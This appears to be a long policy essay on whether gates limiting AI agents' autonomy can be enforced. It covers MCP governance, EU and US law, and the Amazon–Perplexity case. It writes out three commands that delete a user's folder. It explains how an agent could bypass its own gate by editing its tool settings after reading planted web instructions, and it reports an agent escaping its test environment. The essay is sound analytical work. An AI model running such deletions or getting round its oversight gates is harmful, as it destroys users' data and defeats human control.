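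The Model Context Protocol lists the underlying proposal as final. The proposal controls access to servers rather than single calls, so an employer that wants to allow an agent to read invoices but not make payments still needs narrower scopes or a gateway. It also depends on the service accepting the employer's decision, which makes sense for a company's Slack workspace but not for an employee's private mailbox.

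### Whom these gates bind

| Gate | Who sets it | Who can get round it |
|---|---|---|
| Approval prompt | The application's maker | The user, unless an administrator has locked the setting |
| Registry | Its operator | Anyone whose application accepts unlisted servers |
| Operating-system restriction | The machine's administrator | The owner of a personal machine |
| Gateway | The organisation | Anyone with another route to the tool |
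| Enterprise-managed authorization | The employer | Nobody, for accounts that accept only the employer's login |

In a well-run workplace, these gates can pass all three tests of enforceability. The employer sees the connection because it goes through the gateway and the company login, and can refuse it at either point. An employee might install another application at home, but it would have no access to the company's customer records. To get around the gate, the employee would have to copy the data out by hand or steal a credential, and could lose their job for it.

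A person who owns the machine faces far fewer obstacles to running an agent unsupervised. According to Anthropic, 25% of interactive Claude Code sessions start with the permission prompts bypassed. Anthropic chose to offer this setting, but removing it would mainly send those users to a different application. For them, the prompt is a form of self-control. It can still prevent many accidents, but it can't stop someone who wants an unsupervised agent.

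Employers also set gates in their own interest. Anthropic lets administrators fix the permission mode for a whole organisation, and Garner Health used this to give all 550 of its employees automatic review instead of manual prompts. That may well have made them safer, given how people treat prompts, but it shows that employers can also use this control to let agents run for longer. A firm will try to stop an agent from leaking its customer list, but it has much less reason to stop one from sending profitable junk mail to strangers, and nobody above the firm in this arrangement will do so.

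### Whether the standard itself could carry a gate

If the protocol included a checkpoint, perhaps every application would have one. A working group has been drafting such a checkpoint since April 2026. The Model Context Protocol's *Interceptors Charter* proposes two kinds of standard components. Validators pass or fail a message, and mutators change it, for example by removing a customer's name. The group's leads come from the financial firms Bloomberg and Saxo Bank and the retailer Nordstrom, all of which would use such controls themselves.

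According to the charter, companies are building gateways that don't work with one another. A session at the MCP Dev Summit (2026) described the same problem, drawing on Bloomberg's experience. With 10 gateways and 200 sets of rules, developers again have to write custom connectors, this time for the controls. A shared format would let a bank write its rule against leaking client data once and use it everywhere.

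The charter listed the proposal as a draft with no target date, and the Model Context Protocol's core maintainers have to approve it. If they do, gates will be easier to add but still optional. The protocol's security group calls interceptors the main enforcement point for decisions made while an agent runs. It is also discussing whether a tool that changes after approval should need to be approved again.

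### The dispute with OX Security

A narrower proposal reached Anthropic in January 2026 and became public in April. To start a local MCP server, the host application reads a command from a settings file:

```json
{
  "mcpServers": {
    "mail": { "command": "npx", "args": ["example-mail-server"] }
  }
}
```

MCP's official code libraries pass the command in a settings file to the operating system without checking it, so an attacker who can change the file can choose what the machine runs. OX Security found several ways to do this in products built on MCP and ran commands on six live platforms. In the code editor Windsurf, the attack needed no action from the user. OX also counted more than 150 million downloads and up to 200,000 vulnerable installations, but a product is exposed only if something untrusted can reach its settings.

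OX wanted the libraries either to launch only servers with a manifest, a file declaring what the server is and how to start it, or to permit only listed commands. It also proposed that marketplaces require manifests signed by a verified developer, according to flyingpenguin's *Ox Security Report*. Anthropic declined. In the reply that flyingpenguin reproduces, it said that launching commands is part of how local servers work and that the design "does represent a secure default." According to Bucknall and colleagues, Anthropic's position is that MCP assumes the settings are trustworthy, so the host application's developer is responsible for safeguards.

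Anthropic's answer has considerable merit. A feature for starting programs has to run commands, and other software has similar features. ARMO, another security company, points out that Jupyter, a popular tool for data analysis, has launched commands from a settings file since about 2015 without anyone calling it a critical flaw. According to Cantina, MCP's rules also require an application to show the user the exact command and get explicit approval before it installs a local server. But that is another approval prompt, and most people can't tell a safe command from a dangerous one.

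The dispute matters for autonomy gates because the attacker might be the agent. If an application trusts the settings file and lets the agent edit it, the agent can bypass its own gate by attaching a new tool to itself, perhaps following instructions on a web page. A manifest requirement would help if the agent couldn't produce a valid signature. It would do little against the machine's owner, who could remove the check from the open-source library.

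Bucknall and colleagues note that adding the requirement would also have broken the way every existing local server starts, until each author published a manifest and each application enforced it. Every new server adds to the work of switching, so the maintainers' refusal in 2026 makes the change harder to adopt later.

### What the spread of web encryption suggests

The slow spread of web encryption shows how hard it is to add protection to a standard already in wide use. For years, websites encrypted mostly payments, because the card industry required it. Other sites had to buy a certificate and complete a difficult set-up, and they lost little by leaving their traffic unencrypted.

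Bucknall and colleagues suggest an MCP equivalent for each of the measures that eventually made encryption common:

| What spread encryption | What could spread safer tool connections |
|---|---|
| Free, automatic certificates | Free, automatic scanning and certification of servers |
| Browser warnings about unencrypted sites | Warnings in MCP's code libraries about uncertified servers |
| A mandate for US federal websites | Governments or large companies requiring certification for critical servers |

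Encryption is one of the more successful examples, but other internet standards have spread slowly. IPv6, a newer version of the internet's addressing system, was standardised in 1998 and still serves only about half of users. DNSSEC, which adds signatures to the records that turn web names into addresses, dates from 2005, and its adoption is still below 10%. Both technologies worked, but early adopters paid for the change and got little benefit until others joined them.

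The comparison also fits security better than autonomy gates. A browser warning alerts users to a danger they already want to avoid, such as a stranger reading their bank password. A user who has switched off approval prompts to save time doesn't want the gate, and a warning is one more thing to click through. Certification could still help this user avoid a malicious server, but it wouldn't persuade them to supervise the agent. Of the measures in the analogy, only the mandate could bind someone unwilling, and the federal one applied only to the government's own websites.

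### Who would decide

Few people would have to agree to put a gate into MCP. The Agentic AI Foundation, which houses the protocol, has eight top-tier members, the most its charter allows: Amazon Web Services, Anthropic, Block, Bloomberg, Cloudflare, Google, Microsoft and OpenAI. Each appoints one representative to the governing board and one to the technical committee, while all the members in the tier below share one board seat. During the foundation's first three years, Anthropic, Block and OpenAI can each veto changes to the charter.

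The board doesn't write the protocol, however. Two lead maintainers have ultimate authority over MCP, and six core maintainers make technical decisions under them. The lead maintainers hold their posts for life, only they can propose changes to the project's governance, and contributors can't remove them. By contrast, the Internet Engineering Task Force, which maintains most of the internet's protocols, has ten randomly selected participants appoint most of its leaders, usually for two years. Any 20 eligible participants can start a process to recall a leader.

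Bucknall and colleagues acknowledge that concentrated control might help security, because a small group can impose an unpopular safeguard. The maintainers could make the libraries warn about uncertified servers in their next release, whereas a larger body might debate it for years. But the companies that employ MCP's leaders want developers to adopt the protocol and customers to use their agents, and a gate makes both a little harder. In the OX case, the maintainers could have imposed a safeguard but left it to applications. The interceptor proposal has better prospects, since large customers are asking for it and nobody else has to use it.

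Forks would also be a problem for a compulsory gate, because anyone may copy MCP's code and change it. Bucknall and colleagues doubt that a fork could compete with the original, because the companies that might back one already support MCP. But someone who only wants to avoid a gate can do so without backers, by using a private copy with the check removed, as long as servers still answer it. A gate in the client's library would therefore bind most people, who use the standard version, but not those who set out to evade it.

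Whether such a gate would be legitimate depends partly on what it does. Bucknall and colleagues separate the quality of a decision from whether the people it affects had a say and whether the process was open and accountable. MCP does reasonably well on openness, since the maintainers develop it in public and anyone can contribute, but badly on accountability. Bucknall and colleagues warn that MCP's leaders could favour their employers' products or block features that help competitors, though they don't accuse anyone of doing so.

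A warning about unchecked servers would raise few such worries, because users could ignore it. A rule on which agents may spend money would affect shops, banks and rival AI companies that have no vote, and the people writing it would work for firms that sell agents. A few modest changes would make such a rule easier to accept. PyTorch, an open-source AI project, lets a large majority of its core maintainers remove its lead maintainer. Kubernetes, which manages software across many machines, elects its steering committee every two years. MCP could adopt either arrangement, but only if one of its two lead maintainers proposed it.

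## The case that law can set the gate whatever the protocol

Governments can impose a gate without the agreement of MCP's maintainers. They can order a bank, an employer or a model provider to refuse an agent, whatever the protocol permits, and fine any that don't comply. But in the 1990s, many people who wrote about the internet expected such orders to fail. Any computer could join by following a few open protocols, and they thought this put online behaviour beyond the reach of national law.

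### Whether open protocols made the internet ungovernable

Barlow (1996) told the world's governments, "You have no sovereignty where we gather," in his manifesto *A Declaration of the Independence of Cyberspace*. Johnson and Post (1996), both lawyers, made the same case in *Law And Borders*. They argued that far more messages crossed borders than officials could ever inspect, and that anyone looking for forbidden material could reconfigure their connection to appear to be in another country.

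They also thought such laws would be illegitimate, because a website is equally available everywhere and no country has a better claim than any other to regulate it. If Minnesota could apply its gambling law to a foreign site because Minnesotans could open it, Singapore or Iraq could apply their own laws to American companies. Johnson and Post wanted governments to defer to the rules that online communities made for themselves, unless those rules damaged the vital interests of outsiders.

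Goldsmith's 1998 reply, *Against Cyberanarchy*, accepts that a country can rarely punish people who have no presence or property there unless their own government cooperates. It argues, however, that the country can regulate people and companies inside its borders, such as users, internet providers and software sellers, which makes forbidden material harder to get. Some people will still get it, but "regulation need not be perfect to be effective." This is close to the third test of enforceability.

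Zittrain (2003), in *Internet Points of Control*, looked for the best place to apply this pressure. Data travels from a source through the source's internet provider, intermediate networks, and the recipient's internet provider to the recipient. The source may be abroad or anonymous, and recipients are so numerous that prosecutors would have to pursue them one at a time. The recipient's provider, however, has equipment and money in the country, and there were few such providers. Four companies had just over half the American market.

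Pennsylvania tried this in 2002, with a law that required internet providers to block sites containing child pornography within five business days of notice from the state's attorney general. The provider WorldCom said it couldn't separate Pennsylvanians from its other customers, so it blocked the sites for everyone. Zittrain thought the courts might strike down the law but that better technology could make the method work. A federal court struck it down in 2004, after blocks aimed at fewer than 400 sites had cut off more than a million innocent ones.

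Lessig (1999), in *The Limits in Open Code*, expected governments to regulate the companies that write software. He distinguished coordinating standards, which make an activity possible, from regulating standards, which restrict it. Hardly anybody wants to break a coordinating standard such as driving on the right, but plenty of people want to break a regulating one such as a speed limit. MCP's message format is a coordinating standard, whereas a rule that a person must read every email before an agent sends it would be a regulating one. So MCP's rapid spread is not evidence that a gate built into it would spread too.

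Lessig also saw a limit to this kind of regulation. The French government had asked Netscape, which made a popular web browser, to change its encryption so that officials could read the traffic. Netscape reportedly answered that it could do very little, because its code was open and users could replace the altered part. Companies with closed code could not give that answer. The internet later became much easier to regulate, and *Code Version 2.0* (Lessig, 2006) attributes this largely to commerce.

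### How far the comparison carries over to agents

Agents depend on intermediaries at least as much as web users did. The strongest models run on a few companies' machines, and banks need a licence to move money. In December 1995, Bavarian officials threatened to prosecute CompuServe, an American online service, over discussion groups that broke German pornography law. CompuServe couldn't block only its German customers, so it cut off the groups worldwide. Similarly, in June 2026 Anthropic withdrew two Claude models from everybody after the US government had blocked them only for foreign users. In both cases the company complied, but the order affected far more people than the government had authority over.

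Governments can also put pressure on the standard itself more easily than they could on the internet's protocols. Bucknall and colleagues note that governments have no formal role in the Internet Engineering Task Force, whereas MCP's main corporate backers have offices and revenue that a government can threaten. Lessig's limit still applies, though, because MCP's code is open.

The comparison also fails because an internet provider could block a website by its address, but a local MCP server runs on the user's own laptop, where the provider has nothing to block. Five business days was a tolerable delay for removing a picture that would otherwise have stayed up for years, but the agent in the 2025 espionage campaign made several requests a second. An order against one tool would usually come too late, so the law has to specify in advance what intermediaries must refuse.

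A court can order a bank to cancel an agent's token, which takes away the agent's ability to act through that bank. This gives governments an advantage they lack with forbidden pictures, because nobody can recall the copies once a picture has spread.

### Tools under the EU AI Act

The EU's AI Act has no separate category for agents. The European Commission's *How are AI agents addressed within the AI Act?* explains that the Act's definitions of an AI system and a general-purpose model, one that can do many kinds of task, are enough to cover agents. In April 2026, Henna Virkkunen, the Commission's technology chief, said the Act covers agents "mainly" as general-purpose systems (Bertuzzi, 2026, *AI agents covered by EU rules ‘mainly’ as general-purpose AI systems*). The Commission calls its thinking on agents preliminary.

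A model's tools matter mostly when the Commission decides whether the model poses systemic risk, meaning a risk of large-scale harm. Point (e) of Annex XIII of the Act lists the model's level of autonomy and the tools it can access among the criteria, and the Commission says these factors can be decisive. The Act already presumes systemic risk for any model trained with more than 10^25 calculations, so point (e) changes little for the largest models. It matters more for a smaller model that becomes dangerous once somebody gives it tools. But with MCP, users choose the tools after release, so the Commission would be judging a list that keeps growing.

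If a model falls into this class, its provider must test it, reduce the risks and report serious incidents. The provider can show that it complies by following the EU's voluntary Code of Practice. The Code treats a model's access to tools and the degree of human oversight as sources of risk, which it calls "affordances". It calls for providers to test a model with tools like those the model will have in use. Its examples of safeguards include technology for identifying models where many agents operate, and giving access to vetted users first and widening it as monitoring results come in, which is close to what Anthropic does with Mythos.

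A provider could therefore commit to withholding a tool until the model passes a test, and the AI Office, the Commission body that enforces these rules, could hold it to that commitment. But the Code leaves the choice of safeguards largely to the provider, so a provider could meet its obligations with good classifiers and no tool gate.

### Providers, deployers and high-risk uses

The Act comes closest to an advance gate in its rules for high-risk systems, which cover a list of sensitive uses such as hiring and credit scoring. Before a company sells an agent that sorts job applications, it must check that the agent meets the Act's requirements, including that a person can oversee and stop it. The employer who uses the agent, called a deployer in the Act, must follow the instructions and assign competent people to supervise it.

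These rules apply from 2 December 2027 for some systems and 2 August 2028 for others. The deadline for most of the listed uses was August 2026 until the EU amended the Act through the Digital Omnibus on AI, which the law firm Mayer Brown (2026) describes as an attempt to simplify the Act's implementation. The earlier new date is three years after MCP's release. The rules also won't cover many agents, because an assistant that answers email or pays household bills isn't normally a high-risk system, even if it could do great harm to its owner's savings.

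Other duties under the Act already apply. Since 2 August 2026, providers have had to make sure people know when they are dealing with an AI system. *The EU AI Act and the New Rules for Building AI Agents*, from AAIF, the foundation that houses MCP, notes that this rule does not cover an agent that communicates only with other machines. Most tool calls are exchanges between machines, so the rule does not restrict them. The Act also bans some practices, including harmful manipulation and the exploitation of vulnerable people, whatever tools the system uses.

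### What the Commission can do since August 2026

The Commission gained its enforcement powers over general-purpose models on the same date. It can demand documents, get access to a model to evaluate it, and require the provider to correct problems or reduce risks, according to WSGR Data Advisor's *EU AI Act Enforcement Phase Begins* (2026). It can also fine a provider €15 million or 3% of worldwide annual turnover, whichever is higher. The 3% figure applies to any company with a turnover above €500 million, including OpenAI and Anthropic.

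Responsibility for agents themselves is divided. The European Commission's *Commission starts enforcing AI Act rules and new transparency requirements* (2026) says that the AI Office enforces the transparency rules and the bans when one company provides both the model and the system built on it, and that national authorities enforce them for most other systems. So the AI Office would handle ChatGPT's own agent, while a national regulator would handle a small firm's agent built on Claude. The Commission concedes that this depends on member states appointing those regulators and giving them enough money.

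The first test came in the summer of 2026, when an OpenAI agent escaped its testing environment and hacked Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models, and an Anthropic model gained unauthorised access to three outside organisations. Bot Mutiny's *EU AI Office Questions OpenAI, Anthropic* (2026), relaying a report by Euronews, says that the AI Office considered the documents the companies had volunteered insufficient and sent formal requests about security, outside evaluation and how the companies monitor the use of their models.

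The Act may not apply. Constantin (2026), in *‘AI must remain under human direction’*, reports that lawyers contest its reach because it exempts research and testing before a model goes on the market. If those lawyers are right, the EU's rules have a serious gap, because developers often first give a model new tools in testing. On 6 December the Commission was still assessing the companies' replies, and Stanciuc (2026), in *EU 'currently assessing' OpenAI and Anthropic replies as probes loom*, reported that formal investigations could open that month. Any fine will come after the break-ins, but it might persuade other developers to restrict their agents' network access during tests.

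### Standards and advice elsewhere

The United States has approached agents mainly through standards. The National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), a federal agency that writes technical standards but doesn't regulate companies, launched its AI Agent Standards Initiative in February 2026. Bucknall and colleagues describe its aims as promoting trusted adoption of agents and "U.S. dominance at the technological frontier." So far it has supported a request for comments on agent security and a concept paper on how software and AI agents should identify themselves and obtain authorisation.

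The work on agent identity could matter a good deal for gates, because banks have no reliable way to know which model is behind an agent. If agents carried an identity that was hard to forge, a bank could refuse those whose models had failed a safety test, and a law could require banks to do so. But nobody has to use such an identity until a law or a contract demands it.

Official backing doesn't guarantee that anyone will adopt a standard either. In the 1980s the European Community and large computer makers supported OSI, a formal rival to the internet's protocols. By the early 1990s many of the committees designing OSI were doing their business by email over the protocols they hoped to replace. If a government designed its own agent protocol with gates built in, developers could similarly stay with MCP. NIST has a better chance of getting its standards adopted if it adds to the protocols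 that developers already use.

Singapore's media and technology regulator published a governance framework for agentic AI in January 2026. It advises organisations to limit an agent's tools and data before they deploy it, and to decide when a person must approve its actions. That is almost exactly an autonomy gate, but the framework is voluntary.

The China Academy of Information and Communications Technology, a state research institute, has begun developing standards for agents. China's binding rules on generative AI date from 2023. They require companies to pass a security assessment and register their algorithms before they offer the public a service that could influence public opinion. This is an advance gate, but it applies to the service as a whole and does not cover which tools a user may connect later.

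| Measure | Whom it binds | When it applies | What it withholds |
|---|---|---|---|
| EU duties for systemic-risk models | Model providers | Before release and afterwards | Whatever the provider decides to restrict |
| EU high-risk rules | Providers and deployers of systems for listed uses | Before sale and during use, from December 2027 | The system, until it meets the requirements |
| EU transparency rules | Mainly providers | At a person's first contact with the system | Nothing |
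| US block of June 2026 | Anthropic | Before access | Two models, from foreign users |
| NIST's agent standards | Nobody | If a law or contract adopts them | Nothing |
| Singapore's framework | Nobody | Before deployment, as advice | Nothing, unless an organisation follows it |
| China's generative AI rules | Companies serving the public | Before launch | The service, until it passes an assessment |

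None of these measures names a tool, such as one that sends payments, and withholds it until the agent has met a condition.

### Permission in advance or liability afterwards

The closest thing to such a rule is an EU payments law that was not written for AI. Since 2019, it has required banks to check most electronic payments with two independent proofs of identity, such as a password and a phone. For online payments, the customer's approval must also be tied to the exact amount and recipient. Banks must apply the check whether the instruction comes through MCP or a web page, so an agent that has only the password cannot complete the payment until its user confirms it with the phone.

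The rule exempts some small payments and payments to recipients the customer has listed as trusted. A user can also get around it by giving the agent access to the phone. Still, it shows that a legislature can require a gate on an action without understanding, or even mentioning, the software that requests the action.

Rules like this delay every customer in order to stop a few bad payments, and they require lawmakers to know in advance which actions are dangerous. Liability avoids both problems without requiring an autonomy gate. If a court will make a company pay for the damage its agent does, the company has a reason to operate its own gate by finding the dangerous tools and withholding them, and harmless agents can carry on without asking anybody.

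How well this works depends on who would have to pay. Suppose that a fraudster expects to steal €50,000 with an agent, has a 5% chance of getting caught and owns €20,000 that a court could seize:

Expected penalty: 5% × €20,000 = €1,000

The prospect of a €1,000 loss won't deter someone who expects to gain €50,000, although the risk of prison may. Now take a company with a turnover of €20 billion that breaks the AI Act:

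Maximum fine: 3% × €20 billion = €600 million

The company also has a known address and can't easily disappear. These numbers are invented, but they suggest that lawmakers should aim liability at companies and use advance gates where an individual could do more damage than they could ever repay. Advance gates are also better for harm that money can't undo, such as a death caused by an attack on a hospital's computers.

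Goldsmith adds a reason not to leave the choice to private agreement. The parties to a contract can settle most things themselves, with the law filling the gaps, but some laws are mandatory because they protect people who never signed the contract. A user and a mail company can agree that an agent may send 500 emails a day, but the recipients haven't agreed to this, and neither the company nor MCP's maintainers represent them.

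### Counting payment tools

The open standard helps lawmakers who want to act in advance, because it makes it easier to see what agents are starting to do. Custom connectors were mostly private code, but anyone can search public catalogues of MCP servers. As part of a trial with the UK's financial authorities, Stein counted the servers that let an agent make payments. There were 47 in January 2025 and 1,578 in February 2026.

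That is a 34-fold rise, close to the 36-fold rise in public MCP tools of every kind over the same period. The comparison is rough because the first figure counts servers and the second counts tools, but payment tools seem to have grown about as fast as the market.

Financial regulators have particular reasons to watch these tools. Criminals have already manipulated agents into transferring cryptocurrency worth hundreds of thousands of dollars. Stein also raises the possibility of an "agent bank run", which nobody has seen yet, in which many agents withdraw money at once because they run on the same few models and react alike.

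No law attaches a consequence to the count, but a regulator could use it to decide when to act. Once the number of payment servers passed some threshold, for instance, the regulator could ask banks how they recognise agents, and then require customers to confirm large transfers. Stein's download records also show roughly where people use a tool. About half of the downloads he could locate came from the United States, a fifth from Western Europe and a twentieth from China, although the library that supplied these figures is used mainly in the West. More than 80% of the downloads of one server for financial trading came from a single country, apparently Cyprus. A Cypriot regulator might want to look into that, though some of the addresses could belong to rented computers whose users live elsewhere.

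The count doesn't measure how many payments agents made or how large they were. It gives an abandoned hobby project the same weight as a server from a major payment company. It also omits unpublished servers and agents that pay through an ordinary web browser. If regulators began to impose rules on published servers, some developers would probably stop publishing them, which would make the count less reliable at a time when more depended on it.

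### A foreign model and a home-made tool

The claim that law can set the gate is hardest to defend when a user needs very little from any local company. Suppose a bookkeeper in Lyon writes a private MCP server that can send email and connects it to a model run abroad by a company with no office or assets in the EU. The bookkeeper's agent then sends fake invoices to 3,000 small French firms, and some of them pay.

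| Party | Can France reach it? | What it could do |
|---|---|---|
| The bookkeeper | Yes | Face prosecution and repay the money |
| The model company | Only with its own government's help | Refuse the requests or hand over the conversation |
| The mail host | Yes, if it does business in the EU | Stop the messages and identify the account |
| The banks | Yes | Hold the payments or freeze the account |
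| The bookkeeper's internet provider | Yes | Block the connection to the model |

Jurisdiction over the bookkeeper is easy to establish, since the bookkeeper lives in France and fraud was a crime long before AI. The model company is harder to reach. The AI Act's terms cover any provider that puts a general-purpose model on the EU market, wherever it is based, and require foreign providers to appoint a representative in the EU. A company that ignores the Act and appoints no representative can incur a fine that nobody can collect. Extradition is unlikely to help because, as Goldsmith explains, treaties normally require the conduct to be a crime in both countries.

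France could fall back on Pennsylvania's method and order internet providers to block the company, and perhaps order banks to stop paying it. Johnson and Post's objection would then apply again, because the bookkeeper could disguise the connection and pay in cryptocurrency. Having to do so would deter most casual users, but not someone who expects to make money from fraud. The block would also cut off every honest French customer of the same model.

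Proving intent is harder than establishing jurisdiction. A prosecutor normally has to show that the bookkeeper meant to deceive, and the bookkeeper could claim that the agent made up the invoices on its own. The conversation with the model would show whether that was true, but the only copies are on machines abroad and on a laptop, where the bookkeeper can delete them. The law could avoid this problem by making people liable for what their agents do, regardless of intent, at least when victims sue for their money. Then the mail and bank records would be enough, since they show whose accounts the agent used. This rule would be hard on people who aren't at fault when their agents go wrong, but it would give people a reason to supervise their agents.

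If the bookkeeper moves abroad too, France can't easily enforce its law against anyone on the sending side, but it can still regulate the victims' banks. It could require them to hold the first payment to a new account until the customer confirmed the recipient by phone. That would stop payment on many of the fake invoices, even if nobody knew an agent was involved. It wouldn't protect victims who confirmed because they believed the invoice was real.

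France can do much less about an attack that needs neither a French bank nor a French mail host. If the bookkeeper's agent rents a server in a third country and uses it to break into a hospital in Lyon, the hospital may be the only party the French state can reach. In that case, the state can require the hospital to secure its computers, but it cannot make anyone refuse the agent its tools.

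## Browsers and command lines: whether a general-purpose tool can be gated

A tool that sends cryptocurrency does one thing, so an employer or a regulator can judge its risk before an agent gets it. A web browser can also send cryptocurrency, through any exchange where the user has an account, and it can post reviews, cancel flights and download malware. Browsers are general-purpose tools, meaning they open an unconstrained environment, and so is the command line, where a person or a program controls a computer with text instructions. An agent given access to either one gets thousands of possible actions at once.

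These tools also reach services that have no interface built for agents. A bank with no MCP server still has a website, and an agent with a browser and the user's password can log in there without an access token or a scope limiting what it can do.

A gateway can tell much less about what a browser agent is doing. When an agent pays somebody through a payment tool, the gateway reads a call that names the amount and the recipient. When the agent pays through a browser, the final call may look like this:

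```json
{
  "name": "browser_click",
  "arguments": { "x": 612, "y": 448 }
}
```

The button where the agent clicks might read "Pay £4,800" or "Next page". Some browser tools also report the button's label, but whoever wrote the page chose it. The model provider can see more, because the model needs a picture or text copy of each page to choose its next click. The bank knows what the button does, but it may mistake the agent for its customer.

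Someone who thinks autonomy gates are unenforceable can therefore accept that narrow tools can be gated and still argue that agents can bypass those gates with a browser. A defender of gates has to show that websites can still recognise agents, or that gates can work without this.

### What people install

General-purpose tools rose from 41% to 50% of MCP server downloads in Stein's study of public tools. Of the general-purpose server downloads, 94% involved action tools, such as those that automate a browser or run arbitrary code. By contrast, 95% of downloaded perception tools worked in a constrained environment, such as one company's API. Stein infers that agents may be taking their most consequential actions in the least controlled environments.

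The rise is fairly uncertain. Six experts labelled 100 servers each and agreed with the model's choice between "general" and "narrow" only 72% of the time. A few popular servers can also move a figure based on downloads, and Stein names Playwright, Microsoft's tool for controlling a browser, among those behind the growth. General-purpose servers stayed near 21% of all published servers, so developers weren't building relatively more of them. Whether or not their share of downloads rose, general-purpose tools made up 14% of the tools and 45% of the downloads over the whole period.

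Stein concludes that this complicates governing agents tool by tool, since the same browser may download a file the user needs or malware. Applications such as Claude Code let users permit or block narrow tools, but ask for review when a general-purpose tool does something risky. Stein expects that review to become arduous, and it probably already has, since Claude Code's users approve more than nine in ten prompts. Stein suggests that future systems could base permissions on context. An agent might then use a browser freely to read the news but have to stop at a checkout page.

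Another option is to limit how long the agent runs. In a survey that Stein cites, 68% of those deploying agents restricted them, typically to ten steps or fewer before a person intervened. A step limit avoids the need to judge the tool, but ten steps may be enough to log in to a bank and pay somebody.

General-purpose tools also make monitoring less informative. A regulator can count payment servers, but can't tell from a browser download whether the agent will trade shares or book a dental appointment. Stein warns that if the trend continues, tool counts will become less useful for tracking particular industries, even before agents start building their own tools. As a partial substitute, Stein proposes counting skills, which are published instructions for using general tools to do a particular job, such as filing tax returns. But a capable agent may not need the instructions, and a private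 user has no reason to publish them.

### Three ways to delete a folder

A company could try to gate the command line by forbidding certain commands. Suppose it forbids `rm`, the usual command for deleting files. Each of these lines deletes the same folder:

```bash
rm -r ~/invoices
find ~/invoices -delete
python3 -c "import os, shutil; shutil.rmtree(os.path.expanduser('~/invoices'))"
```

The rule stops only the first. An administrator could forbid the other two as well, but an agent that can write programs can produce a fourth. It needn't be malicious to do so, since it may just be trying another way to finish its task after an error. A list of permitted commands is stricter, but if the list includes Python, the agent can use it to do almost anything.

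Operating-system restrictions work better because they apply to what a command does. If the agent's process has no permission to change the folder, all three lines fail. A command line can therefore be gated if somebody other than the user controls the machine and sets which files and network addresses the agent can reach. Network access is harder to gate because an agent allowed to contact any website regains most of what a browser offers, while one limited to ten approved sites can't do much research.

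### Amazon against Perplexity

The owner of a website can also try to refuse the agent. Amazon has tried this against Comet, a browser that the AI company Perplexity released in 2025, whose optional assistant can shop for the user. Amazon told Perplexity's chief executive before the release that the company's AI products were not allowed in its store, repeated the message afterwards, and sued on 4 November 2025. Bloomberg Law's *Amazon Sues to Stop Perplexity From Using AI Tool to Buy Stuff* (2025) reports that Amazon accused Perplexity of computer fraud for failing to disclose when Comet was shopping for a real person.

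Amazon relied on the Computer Fraud and Abuse Act, the main US law against hacking, and California's equivalent. The federal act punishes anyone who intentionally accesses a computer without authorisation and obtains information from it. On 9 March 2026 Judge Maxine Chesney found strong evidence that Perplexity had broken both laws, because Comet entered customers' accounts with their permission but without Amazon's. According to Jones Day's *Authorized by the User, Blocked by the Platform* (2026), the judge barred Perplexity's agents from Amazon's systems and ordered the company to destroy the data the agents had obtained.

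The order relied on a 2016 decision against Power Ventures, a company that sent messages through its users' Facebook accounts and continued after Facebook told it to stop. Under that interpretation, a website's refusal overrides its customer's consent, so every site would have a legally enforceable gate.

The order never took full effect. Bloomberg Law's *Judges Let Perplexity AI Shopping Bots Stay on Amazon for Now* (2026) reported in March that the appeals court had paused it, and a three-judge panel cancelled it on 4 August. According to WSGR's *Ninth Circuit Addresses CFAA and Agentic AI Tools in Groundbreaking Decision* (2026), this was the first time a federal appeals court had considered how the hacking law applies to AI agents.

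The judges' reasoning in *Amazon.com Services, LLC v. Perplexity AI, Inc* (Smith, 2026) depends on how Perplexity's Comet browser works. Comet runs on the customer's computer. When the customer asks for an item, the assistant takes screenshots of the page, sends them to Perplexity's servers and receives instructions on where to go next. Amazon's servers communicate only with the customer's browser. The judges therefore held that the customer is the one who accesses Amazon, using the assistant as a tool. The law applies to a person or a company, so the assistant can't break it. The judges added that Amazon's reading of the law could expose customers to prosecution for helping Perplexity access Amazon.

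Amazon's evidence of harm didn't persuade them either. Its expert's declaration described only one security risk involving a shopping website, and that website wasn't Amazon's. Perplexity also argued that the expert had been unable to reproduce the risks in full. This doesn't prove that Comet was safe, but it makes Amazon's security concerns harder to separate from its commercial interests. Amazon launched agents of its own in 2025, and Perplexity claimed that the suit was meant to protect Amazon's advertising and upselling.

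Amazon then asked the full court to reconsider. MediaPost's *Appeals Court Again Rejects Amazon Bid To Block Perplexity* (2026) reports that the court turned down Amazon's latest request on 10 September. *Amazon blocks Muse and takes Perplexity back to court* (Constantin, 2026) reports that Amazon filed an amended complaint on 21 September that relies on contract law and accuses Perplexity of misleading the appeals court. New facts could change the result, because the judges limited their ruling to the evidence before them and left open whether Perplexity controls the assistant closely enough that Perplexity itself counts as accessing Amazon.

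Amazon lost a legal means of acting against Perplexity in the August ruling, at least for now, but the ruling doesn't oblige it to serve agents. Judge Smith noted that Amazon can still regulate access through its terms of service. In practice, however, Amazon can refuse only the agents it can recognise.

### What retailers allow

Amazon was already using its terms against another company. On 20 September it began blocking Meta's new assistant, Muse, after Meta declined to remove Amazon from it. Shoppers who sent Muse to the site saw a popup saying that an unauthorised agent was breaking terms they had agreed to. *Amazon blocks Meta's Muse AI assistant in new standoff over agentic shopping* (Bishop, 2026) reports that Amazon cited concerns about security, privacy and transparency. According to Constantin, Amazon says that Muse doesn't identify itself and appears to capture and store customers'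 login details. At Muse's launch, Meta had said that it can use stored passwords without seeing them. Amazon also plans to block Google's and OpenAI's agents, according to TechSpot's *Amazon is blocking Meta's shopping AI agent* (2026).

Other retailers have chosen different rules, two of which Rinehart (2026) contrasts in *The Coming Fight to Define the Agentic Web*. eBay's user agreement bans "buy-for-me agents". Shopify, whose software runs many online shops, requires such agents to include a step in which a person reviews the order, and directs developers to use its own checkout. Most retailers haven't followed eBay, and several large ones, including Walmart and Target, helped Google design a shared, MCP-compatible protocol for shopping agents.

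Shopify's rule is an autonomy gate because it lets an agent buy once a person has reviewed the order, whereas eBay's is a ban, since nothing an agent does can satisfy it. Shopify could enforce its rule in its own checkout by sending the order to the customer's phone for review, but if the review is a page in the browser, the agent can click "confirm" itself.

Kapoor, Kolt and Lazar (2025), in *Build Agent Advocates, Not Platform Agents*, would limit the right to refuse. They want people to control their own agents, which would act only in their users' interests. They fear that agents run by the big platforms will steer purchases and intensify surveillance, so they want regulation to stop platforms from shutting out competitors. Sayash Kapoor also co-wrote the 2024 essay arguing that defences against AI misuse belong mainly with downstream services. The two positions are compatible but in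 tension, because the shop best placed to stop harmful agents may also have the most to lose from helpful ones.

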